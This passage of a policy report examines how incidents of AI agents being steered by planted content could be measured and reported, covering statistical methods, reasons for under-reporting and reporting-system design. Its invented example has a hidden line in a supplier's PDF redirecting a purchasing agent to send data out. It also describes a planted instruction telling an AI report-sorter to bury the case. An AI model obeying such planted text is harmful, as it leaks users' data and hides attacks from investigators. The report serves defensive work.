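The phases are meant to guide policy. A rare type of incident might need only monitoring, while one that is growing quickly could justify mandatory reporting or audits. Based on public evidence, steering incidents with confirmed harm would fall in one of the first two phases, but that evidence is too limited to show whether they are rare or often go undetected.

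### The test on autonomous vehicles

Autonomous vehicles offer a rare chance to test these methods because California requires companies testing the vehicles on public roads to report every collision within ten days and their mileage every year. Abraham and colleagues compared these compulsory reports with the AI Incident Database, which relies on the media. The database had 75 incidents from July 2014 to February 2025. They took an average of 170 days to appear, but the fitted delay curve implies a median of only about 17 days, so a few very late entries account for much of the average.

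The two sources barely agreed. From January 2019 on, their monthly counts had a correlation of 0.123, where 0 means no linear relationship and 1 a perfect one. Shifting one series by up to six months to allow for late reporting raised this only to 0.199. The phases matched in 15.3% of months, compared with 9.7% expected by chance. This gives a Cohen's kappa of 0.062, where 0 means chance agreement and 1 perfect agreement. The pattern changed at five points in the compulsory reports, and only two of these appeared in the media-based series. The paper counts 85 months in this comparison, although its stated dates span 74.

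The sources may disagree partly because they cover different incidents. The database includes incidents outside California and incidents involving Tesla cars under human supervision, while the state's records include collisions too minor for newspapers to report.

The raw number of incidents was flat from December 2020 to November 2024, while incidents per million miles appeared to fall. Abraham and colleagues take this as a sign that wider deployment rather than worsening safety explains the number of incidents. But the fall was not statistically significant (p = 0.274), so it could easily be due to chance.

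The researchers conclude that a model can't determine the phase from media reports alone and that experts should interpret its output. To illustrate this, they read the incident reports without the state's data and identified three turning points: Waymo's first incident in California, the arrival of its competitor Cruise, and Cruise's withdrawal. This is weak evidence for expert judgement because they already knew the industry's history. A stronger test would be to give the same reports to several independent panels and compare their answers.

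### Comparing trends instead of totals

*A Pragmatic Classification Framework for AI Incident Monitoring* (Mengesha, Owen and colleagues, 2026) avoids some of these problems by comparing two periods. An analyst first writes a precise question in the form "Among [subjects] that [have an opportunity for harm], how many [events] per [period]?" For steering, the question could be "Among purchasing agents that read suppliers' documents, how many sessions per quarter sent data to an address found only in such a document?"

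The analyst then estimates the harm and the exposure in each period. The best evidence is a direct measurement from an authoritative source, followed by a combination of indirect measures and then expert judgement. If the experts' range spans more than a factor of 100, or they can't agree, the analyst declines to give an estimate. The two trends lead to one of these classes:

| | Exposure falling | Exposure rising |
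|---|---|---|
| Harm per use rising | Concentrating | Escalating |
| Harm per use falling | Receding | Mitigating |

If the evidence can't establish both trends, the result is "unclassifiable".

Comparing trends helps if the reporting bias is stable. Suppose reports double while use triples. If people report the same share of cases in both periods, harm per use has fallen by a third, and the trajectory is "mitigating". But if the share reported has halved, the number of cases has quadrupled, harm per use has risen by a third, and the trajectory is "escalating".

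Mengesha and colleagues also simulate how errors in the estimates affect the result. If harm per use appears to have risen by 50%, but each of the four estimates behind that figure could be wrong by a factor of two, the chance that it really rose is only about 70%.

A case study on chatbots and self-harm shows how a few entries can account for most of a total. An AI search of the AI Incident Database found two matching entries for 2024, with an estimated two cases, and 12 for 2025, with an estimated 10,014 to 110,025. Nine of the 12 described individuals or safety tests, so most of the 2025 figure probably came from the other three, which summarised many cases at once. One of these was based on a statement by OpenAI about its users. Similarly, one vendor publishing the results of a thorough search for steered sessions could suddenly make the whole industry's record look worse.

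### Testing reports as they arrive

Dai, Raji and colleagues (2025), in *Aggregated Individual Reporting for Post-Deployment Evaluation*, propose collecting reports from people affected by a particular AI system and acting when a pattern emerges. They contrast two American databases. The Consumer Financial Protection Bureau passes each complaint to the bank concerned, which must respond to that customer. The vaccine database VAERS is used to find side effects that appear unusually often across all reports. A vendor that, like the Bureau, handles each complaint about its agent separately could miss an attack that affects many customers. As of June 2025, Dai, Raji and colleagues knew of no public system like VAERS in mainstream use for AI.

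Someone who checks the reports every day has many chances to mistake noise for a pattern. Sequential tests limit the chance of ever raising a false alarm, however often someone looks. In *From Individual Experience to Collective Evidence*, Dai, Gradu and colleagues (2025) use them to test whether a group's share of reports is much larger than its share of all users.

One version works like a series of bets. Suppose a vendor monitors 20 connectors, and one of them handles 10% of sessions. The test asks whether it accounts for more than twice that share of reports, or 20%:

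1. The vendor starts with an imaginary stake of 1.
2. Each report about the connector multiplies the stake by 1.8, and each report about another connector multiplies it by 0.8.
3. If the connector's true share of reports is 20%, the stake stays level on average, because 0.2 × 1.8 + 0.8 × 0.8 = 1.
4. The vendor raises an alarm when the stake passes 200, which is 20 connectors divided by an accepted 10% chance of any false alarm.

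If half of all reports concerned the connector, this would take about 30 reports. The published test also adjusts the bet sizes as it goes.

A vendor can learn something about risk from an alarm if it can put an upper limit on how much reporting habits differ. If a connector has twice the average rate of reports, and its cases are at most 25% more likely than average to be reported, its true risk is at least 2 / 1.25 = 1.6 times the average.

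Dai, Gradu and colleagues ran three versions of the test on VAERS reports of myocarditis, an inflammation of the heart muscle, after COVID-19 vaccination. All three flagged men aged 18 to 29 first, after between 34 and 111 reports. With the reports in their original order, the alarms would have come between 22 February and 20 April 2021. But the researchers already knew which side effect to examine and could estimate each group's share of vaccinations from government data. A vendor knows how often customers use each of its connectors, but the people who run an outside database usually don't.

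### What carries over to steering

Researchers have no agreed measure of exposure to steering, and the choice can reverse the result. In this invented example, the number of cases doubles:

| | First quarter | Second quarter | Cases per unit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Confirmed cases | 10 | 20 | |
| Sessions | 1 million | 2 million | Unchanged |
| Outside documents read | 10 million | 40 million | Halved |
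| Planted instructions read | 1,000 | 1,000 | Doubled |

A deployer that wants to know the risk of each task needs the incident rate per session. The rate per planted instruction better measures how well agents resist attacks, but calculating it requires finding the instructions that agents ignored. Anyone who publishes a rate should state which measure they used.

Unlike a drug's side effects, attacks also change in response to monitoring. An attacker who learns that one connector is under investigation can switch to another. An attacker can also start copying files instead of deleting them, which lowers the share of cases that people report. If the number of cases doubled while that share halved, the number of reports would stay the same. Comparing trends therefore works less well for steering than for accidents.

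Some reports may be deliberately false. Dai, Raji and colleagues mention review bombing, in which a crowd floods a website with hostile reviews. A competitor could file a dozen invented complaints about the email connector to create a false signal. An attacker could also hide a real signal by filing 240 complaints about failed logins, which would push the ratio below 2, as in the earlier example. Analysts can repeat the calculation using only reports that match an entry in a trajectory log, although this would exclude reports from honest users whose vendor keeps no such log.

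One planted page can also produce many reports that look independent. Suppose ten of the 12 complaints about the email connector came from agents that had read the same page. If the analyst counts those ten as one, three of 51 reports mention unrequested messages. The ratio falls from 9.7 to 2.9, and chi-squared falls to 3.4, below the usual threshold. The page would still be a serious problem, but the analyst would have much less reason to blame the connector.

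Counting a planted page only once hides how many people it affected, so a database should record both the number of separate attacks and the number of steered sessions. Analysts can also account for links between entries when they calculate uncertainty. Kumar and colleagues found real harm in 24% of the registry entries in which a generative system acted. Treating the entries as independent gave a range of 20 to 29%, but resampling entries from the same website as a block widened it to 15 to 38%. Entries about the same planted page would need similar treatment.

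No published study appears to have applied disproportionality analysis, capture–recapture, sequential tests or incident phases to reports of prompt injection. Kumar and colleagues come closest, with a registry that labels cases of indirect prompt injection, but they decline to estimate how often agents fail. Public databases have too few confirmed cases of steering for most of these methods.

A large vendor could begin with its own data, because it knows how much customers use its agents and can check reports against its logs. It could first test capture–recapture on a known number of cases. With customers' consent, it could plant harmless instructions in their documents until the instructions had steered 100 sessions, then count how many of those sessions were found by its detectors and how many were reported by users. A capture–recapture estimate far below 100 would show that detectors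 and users tend to find the same cases.

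## Designing a reporting system that people will use

A company that learns an agent was steered often has little to gain by telling anyone. In the invented purchasing case, a report could expose the vendor to claims from the manufacturer and from the 120 people in the file, while much of the benefit would go to competitors whose agents might read the same PDF. A reporting system has to either make reporting worthwhile for the vendor or require it.

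### Why people keep known cases to themselves

No published survey appears to cover why companies don't report steered agents, so the evidence comes from related fields. *Understanding Human and Interface Design Factors in Canadian Cybercrime Reporting* (2026) surveyed 204 people, who had reported 127 of the 411 cyber incidents they had experienced (31%). Their most common reasons for not reporting were that the incident wasn't serious enough (24%), that they didn't know where to report it (22%) and that reporting wouldn't help (20%). The respondents were private individuals, so their answers are weak evidence about companies that fear a lawsuit.

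Employees who are willing to report incidents may also be unsure what to report or how to report it. *When technology is not enough* (2025) describes interviews with staff at an industrial firm. Most said they would feel safe reporting a security incident, but most knew only how to report phishing emails and were unsure what else was worth reporting. A buyer who notices a strange message from the purchasing assistant could easily not know whether or how to report it.

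For companies, liability seems to matter more. Wei and Heim (2026), in *Designing Incident Reporting Systems for Harms from General-Purpose AI*, reviewed reporting in nine safety-critical US industries and found that people and companies commonly give legal uncertainty and fear of liability as top reasons for not reporting. In one survey they cite, 72% of physicians said they would be more likely to report an incident if courts couldn't demand the report as evidence, though what they would actually do may differ. Some firms also deliberately keep fewer records because they fear lawsuits, so evidence can be missing before anyone decides whether to report.

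Trade secrets are a particular problem when reporting AI flaws. Bieringer and colleagues argue in *Mind the Gap* that a researcher can usually share the faulty part of a publicly available program, but reproducing an AI flaw may require the model or its data, which the owner keeps confidential. To explain the purchasing case fully, the vendor might have to reveal its system prompt and the manufacturer's prices. *Scheming in the wild* (2026), which collected reports of AI misbehaviour from the social network X, suggests that confidentiality may stop professional developers from sharing transcripts, but it did not measure this effect.

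There are also more mundane obstacles to reporting. *Incorporating AI Incident Reporting into Telecommunications Law and Policy* (2025), which concerns India, lists damage to a company's reputation, low awareness and a lack of incentives. Filing reports also takes effort. Wei and Heim count at least 45 cyber-incident reporting requirements across 22 US federal agencies, some of which duplicate each other. When the cause of an incident is uncertain, the vendor and the model developer can each decide that the other should report it.

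Grosse, Bieringer and colleagues (2024), in *When Your AI Becomes a Target*, combined earlier and newly collected reports into a set of 32 AI security incidents. This work predates most of today's agents. Published accounts left out crucial details about the company and its AI application, and many incidents stemmed from a failure to follow established security and privacy practices. Reporting such an incident would reveal the company's own lapse, which gives it a reason to stay silent. Of the nine incident collections that Bieringer and colleagues compare, the 32-incident set was the only one to use anonymous reports.

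These pressures affect both how many cases become public and which ones. According to Mengesha and colleagues, a public database is most likely to include cases of dramatic harm to a vocal, well-resourced, English-speaking victim in a regulated sector. A case in which a quotation file is quietly copied has almost none of those features.

### Seven design choices

Wei and Heim describe reporting systems along seven dimensions. They exclude attacks that compromise an AI system, so applying their framework to steering goes beyond what they claim. The last column contains this report's suggestions.

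| Dimension | Options | Possible choice for steering |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | Learning from incidents, or holding someone accountable | Learning, with penalties left to existing authorities |
| Reporters and recipients | Companies, employees, users, victims or outsiders, reporting to a company, a government body or a third party | Anyone who sees part of a case, reporting to a body that can't fine them |
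| Event type | Safety, rights or security | All three in one record |
| Stage of risk | Hazard, situation, near miss or harm | Near misses and harm, with links to vulnerability records |
| Compulsion | Voluntary or mandatory | Mandatory for serious harm, voluntary at first for the rest |
| Anonymity | Open, confidential or anonymous | Confidential, with an anonymous route for employees |
| Action after a report | Information sharing, public disclosure, audit or regulatory action | Fast private warnings, then later publication |

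The choice of purpose affects most of the other design choices. Few systems aim at both learning and accountability, because a company won't volunteer its mistakes to an agency that might fine it. Regulators can also have a reason not to ask for reports if a high number would make them look bad. Wei and Heim therefore see advantages in having a voluntary system run by a body with no power to punish.

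Several kinds of reporter are useful even when they describe the same event. In the longer version of their paper, Wei and Heim cite an estimate that 91% of collisions between wildlife and commercial aircraft are reported to the US Federal Aviation Administration (FAA). Most reports come through one central system, but at least ten others contribute. Air traffic staff supplied 7% of the reports in the database and added information to another 7% that also came from other sources. In the purchasing case, the vendor could report what the assistant read, and the manufacturer could report that the file left its systems. Whoever receives the two reports could match them by the time and the outside address.

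In confidential reporting, the recipient knows who sent a report but keeps the name from others. This suits steering incidents better than full anonymity because an investigator may need to ask the reporter for a missing log entry. An employee who fears retaliation from the vendor may still need to report anonymously.

*Known Unknowns and Unknown Unknowns* (Gailmard, Spence and colleagues, 2025) proposes an adverse-event system for AI that combines compulsory and voluntary reports, modelled on the systems that collect reports of harm from drugs, vehicles and other products. Companies would have to report a narrow set of severe events, and anyone could report lesser ones. The paper recommends starting with a narrow definition, because a broad one could overwhelm an agency with poor reports, and widening it as the agency gains experience.

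Gailmard and colleagues would also give companies reasons to take part. A safe harbour would protect a company from punishment if it reported promptly and openly, unless it had been wilfully negligent or committed misconduct. The company could also get pooled industry data, comparisons with other companies or technical help in return for its reports. The purchasing assistant's vendor might benefit most from a list of document hashes and outside addresses from other vendors' cases, which it could search for in its own logs.

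Gailmard and colleagues compare 11 reporting systems. Several protect reporters from civil liability, while the AI Incident Database offers no formal protection. Gailmard and colleagues acknowledge that voluntary systems miss many events even when they protect reporters. Reporting also depends on people recognising that a reportable event has occurred, which is especially hard when retrieved content has steered an agent.

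Some evidence suggests that mandatory reporting changes behaviour. Wei and Heim cite a 2023 study by Kesari, which found that requiring companies to report data breaches to state attorneys general reduced consumers' complaints of identity theft by an average of 10.1%. Some states exempted breaches of encrypted data, and companies there didn't report thefts even when the thief had also taken the encryption key. Complaints about data breaches fell by 13.1% in states that closed this loophole. A rule on steered agents that exempted "authorised access" could create a similar loophole, because a steered agent may be using its own valid account, as the purchasing assistant was.

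### What aviation offers

The US Aviation Safety Reporting System (ASRS) is the usual model for voluntary reporting. The FAA regulates airlines, but it chose NASA, which doesn't, to run ASRS. NASA removes identifying details from reports, and with certain exceptions the FAA can't use a report to punish the person who filed it. The FAA also involved the industry in the design from early on. According to Wei and Heim, ASRS has received more than two million reports since 1975, or roughly 40,000 a year, and has revealed safety information that wasn't available from other sources. This suggests that people trust and use the system, but it doesn't show how many accidents ASRS prevented, because aviation became safer for many other reasons over the same period.

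The EU's Regulation 376/2014 shows that a system can require reports and still protect the people who make them. Pustozerova and colleagues explain that it combines compulsory and voluntary reports with mandatory removal of identifying details and a "just culture". This means staff aren't punished for honest mistakes, but can be for gross negligence or deliberate violations. Pustozerova and colleagues suggest a similar approach for reports under Article 73 of the AI Act.

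Copying the ASRS model hasn't always worked. The US Federal Railroad Administration set up a confidential system that NASA also runs, but only 23 of 800 railway companies joined, and some later left because they found it ineffective. Wei and Heim doubt that AI developers would join more readily. Developers compete intensely and guard technical details, and their products cause harm in many industries. Labour unions, which help run another of the FAA's voluntary programmes, barely exist in the AI industry.

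The protection would also have to cover different risks, because a pilot mainly fears losing a licence, whereas the vendor fears a lawsuit from its customer. Shielding the vendor from all claims would leave the 120 people to bear the losses from its mistakes. A narrower rule could keep the report itself out of court while leaving the logs and the PDF available as evidence. The vendor would then be no worse off for having reported, and the victims would keep their claims.

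The most important difference is that aviation reports rarely concern an adversary who may read them. A published account of a confusing runway sign helps pilots, and there is no attacker to adapt to it. Publishing an account of the supplier's hidden line, however, could teach other attackers how to write one and show the original attacker which wording to abandon.

Removing identifying details from a report is hard because other vendors can need those same details to find the attack. If a PDF steered an agent to contact an outside address, another vendor needs the PDF's hash and that address to search its logs. But an attacker who sent each customer a slightly different PDF could use the hash to work out which customer had reported it. The report's recipient could instead compare hashes privately, so that a vendor learns of a match only if its own agents have read the same file.

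### Whether to wait for serious harm

The main dispute is whether to require reports only after serious harm, as most current laws do, or also after confirmed steering and significant near misses. In Bloomberg Government's *Tracking Corporate AI Threats Via Federal Database Gains Support* (2025), Adam Thierer of the R Street Institute, a US think tank, warns that sweeping requirements would burden companies, produce information of little use and create a risk of litigation. He favours focusing on critical incidents.

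One argument for waiting is the volume of reports. If the invented vendor's detector catches nine steered sessions a day, it catches 3,285 a year. A hundred such vendors would produce 328,500 reports a year, about eight times ASRS's yearly average, not counting near misses. At an hour each, reading them would take nearly 200 full-time staff. Agencies don't have such resources. Gailmard and colleagues note that the US AI Safety Institute had a budget of $10 million for the 2024 fiscal year. If staff can't read all the reports, the few about a death or a power cut may wait in the same queue as the rest.

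A harm trigger is also harder to avoid. People outside the company usually learn of a death, whereas the vendor confirms steering by running replays. If confirmation created a duty to report, a vendor could escape the duty by never running replays, so a rule meant to reveal more cases could lead to fewer investigations. Finally, each extra report could leak and teach someone an attack.

Those who want earlier reports can reply that if reports are required only after harm, warnings will come too late or never. The theft in the purchasing case probably doesn't meet the AI Act's threshold, so other vendors would hear nothing under Article 73 even after the stranger's message. If the same PDF were used to steal a small file from each of a thousand companies, there might still be no single serious incident. The difference between harm and a near miss can also be luck, since the hidden line is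 just as dangerous when one customer's mail filter happens to stop the email.

Near misses are also far more common than severe cases, so people can learn from them sooner. Wei and Heim cite a hospital study which found that 82% of reported safety incidents caused no harm, 18% caused minor or temporary harm and fewer than 1% caused major harm. Another estimate is that near misses occur up to 300 times as often as harmful events. These figures come from medicine, where near misses are mostly accidents. The ratio could be much higher for agents, because attackers can send planted instructions by the thousand at almost no cost.

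Caroline Jeanmarie of the Future Society, a non-profit that works on AI governance, responds to the concern about litigation by saying that taking part in a reporting system gives a company evidence of due diligence. Ben Colman, who runs a company that detects deepfakes, adds that when organisations hide a breach, only the attackers know about it. But hiding a breach can also keep the method from people who might copy it. Sidhu and colleagues point out that the deception category in California's SB 53 is a precedent for triggering a report before harm occurs.

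The value of an early warning depends on whether attackers reuse their attacks. They might, since many of the successful attacks in the public competition described earlier also worked on other models. A report of an instruction written for a single company would give other companies much less to search for.

The two sides disagree less than they seem to. Jeanmarie would make reports compulsory only for high-consequence events and leave near misses to voluntary reports. It is sensible to require a full report after serious harm, because serious harm justifies the effort and is hard to conceal. But the system should also cover less serious incidents, since the information that would protect other companies often exists before anyone suffers serious harm.

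### A staged system

A staged system would ask for less information about less serious events. The version below is this reference's own proposal.

| Event | What to send | Recipient | Timing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Serious harm that steering probably caused | A short notice, then a full account | The responsible authority | The legal deadline |
| A sensitive action directed by outside content, including an attempt that only the last safeguard stopped | The content hash, the destination, the tool used and whether the action succeeded | A confidential clearing house with no power to fine | Within a week |
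| Routine blocks | Total blocks and total sessions | The same clearing house | Every quarter |

The purchasing theft would fall in the second row, and so would the variant in which the manufacturer's mail filter stopped the email. If a classifier had removed the hidden line before the assistant read it, the vendor would only add the attempt to its quarterly count.

The second row doesn't require the vendor to confirm the cause. It could apply whenever an agent tries to send data to a destination that appears only in outside content, unless the user asked for it. The log would show this without a replay, so the vendor couldn't avoid a report by declining to investigate. It could still avoid one by keeping no log, so the system would also need minimum logging rules.

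Sending one notice per planted document instead of one per session would cut the 328,500 reports to about 33,000 if each document steered ten sessions on average. Software could match most of these reports by hash, leaving staff to read those that described a new method or affected several vendors.

The second row could begin as a voluntary scheme with legal protection. MITRE already runs a site where companies can confidentially report attacks on AI, according to Anti-Corruption Report's *From CEO Deepfakes to AI Slop, AI Incident Tracking Ramps Up*. But the failure of the railway scheme is a reason to set a date for reviewing participation. If audits then showed that vendors were reporting only a small share of the cases they knew about, legislators could make the notices compulsory. *The California Report on Frontier AI Policy* (Bommasani, Singer and colleagues, 2025) similarly advises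 policymakers to make sure they can change thresholds over time, including the measures those thresholds use.

The clearing house should also release information in stages. It could privately send hashes and addresses within hours to vendors whose agents might have read the same content, describe the weakness to affected vendors while they work on a fix, and publish a general account later. Publication can't always wait for a complete fix, because models may remain partly susceptible, so it should have a fixed deadline.

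### When the reports become a target

Reports can contain the same sensitive material as the logs they draw on, so a database of them would be valuable to a thief. Pustozerova and colleagues recommend standard categories instead of free text, partly because information is easier to hide in long reports. If the vendor used a compromised agent to draft its report, the agent could hide a customer's prices in the wording without readers noticing.

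Planted text can steer an agent that processes reports, just as it can steer one that searches logs. Suppose the supplier's PDF contained a second hidden instruction for any AI reader to mark the case as a duplicate. If the clearing house used an agent to sort its reports, the PDF could hide the theft from investigators as well as from the buyer. This agent should have the limits already suggested for log-searching agents. It should also work only with structured fields, with the original text in a separate file that it can't open, and a person should approve closing any case.

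Attackers can also plan around a reporting rule. If a report were due only when a theft affected at least 100 people, an attacker could take the details of 99 at a time. Pustozerova and colleagues warn more generally that someone who knows the scheme could design an attack that doesn't show up in incident reports. The clearing house could keep some of its criteria for follow-up private, and count together small cases that share an address or a document. The legal threshold has to be public so that companies know when to report.

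Some attackers might want the victim to file a report. Pustozerova and colleagues describe an attack on a system with mandatory reporting in which the attacker's only aim is to make the victim disclose confidential information. A competitor could steer the purchasing assistant into a reportable failure, then wait for the vendor's account of the assistant's system prompt and safeguards. To prevent this, the vendor should preserve all the evidence but report only what the recipient needs. An investigator could inspect the rest on the vendor's premises, and the public version could leave out the design details.

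Publishing only totals does not fully protect the companies that report. Suppose a competitor files 11 false reports of thefts involving purchasing agents in one quarter, and the clearing house announces a total of 12. The competitor now knows that exactly one other company reported a theft, and may be able to guess which. Checking reports against logs before counting them would make this harder.

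The clearing house could also add random noise to each total, a method known as differential privacy. For two sets of reports, D and D′, that differ by one report, the method guarantees that

P(published result from D) ≤ e^ε × P(same result from D′)

A smaller ε gives stronger privacy. At ε = 0.5, the published total can change the competitor's estimate of the odds that the twelfth report exists by a factor of at most about 1.65. The noise this requires would move a count by two on average. That hardly matters for a total of 500 blocked emails, but it could hide the first three cases of a new attack. The clearing house should therefore use noisy totals to show broad trends, and warn the affected vendors directly about rare cases.
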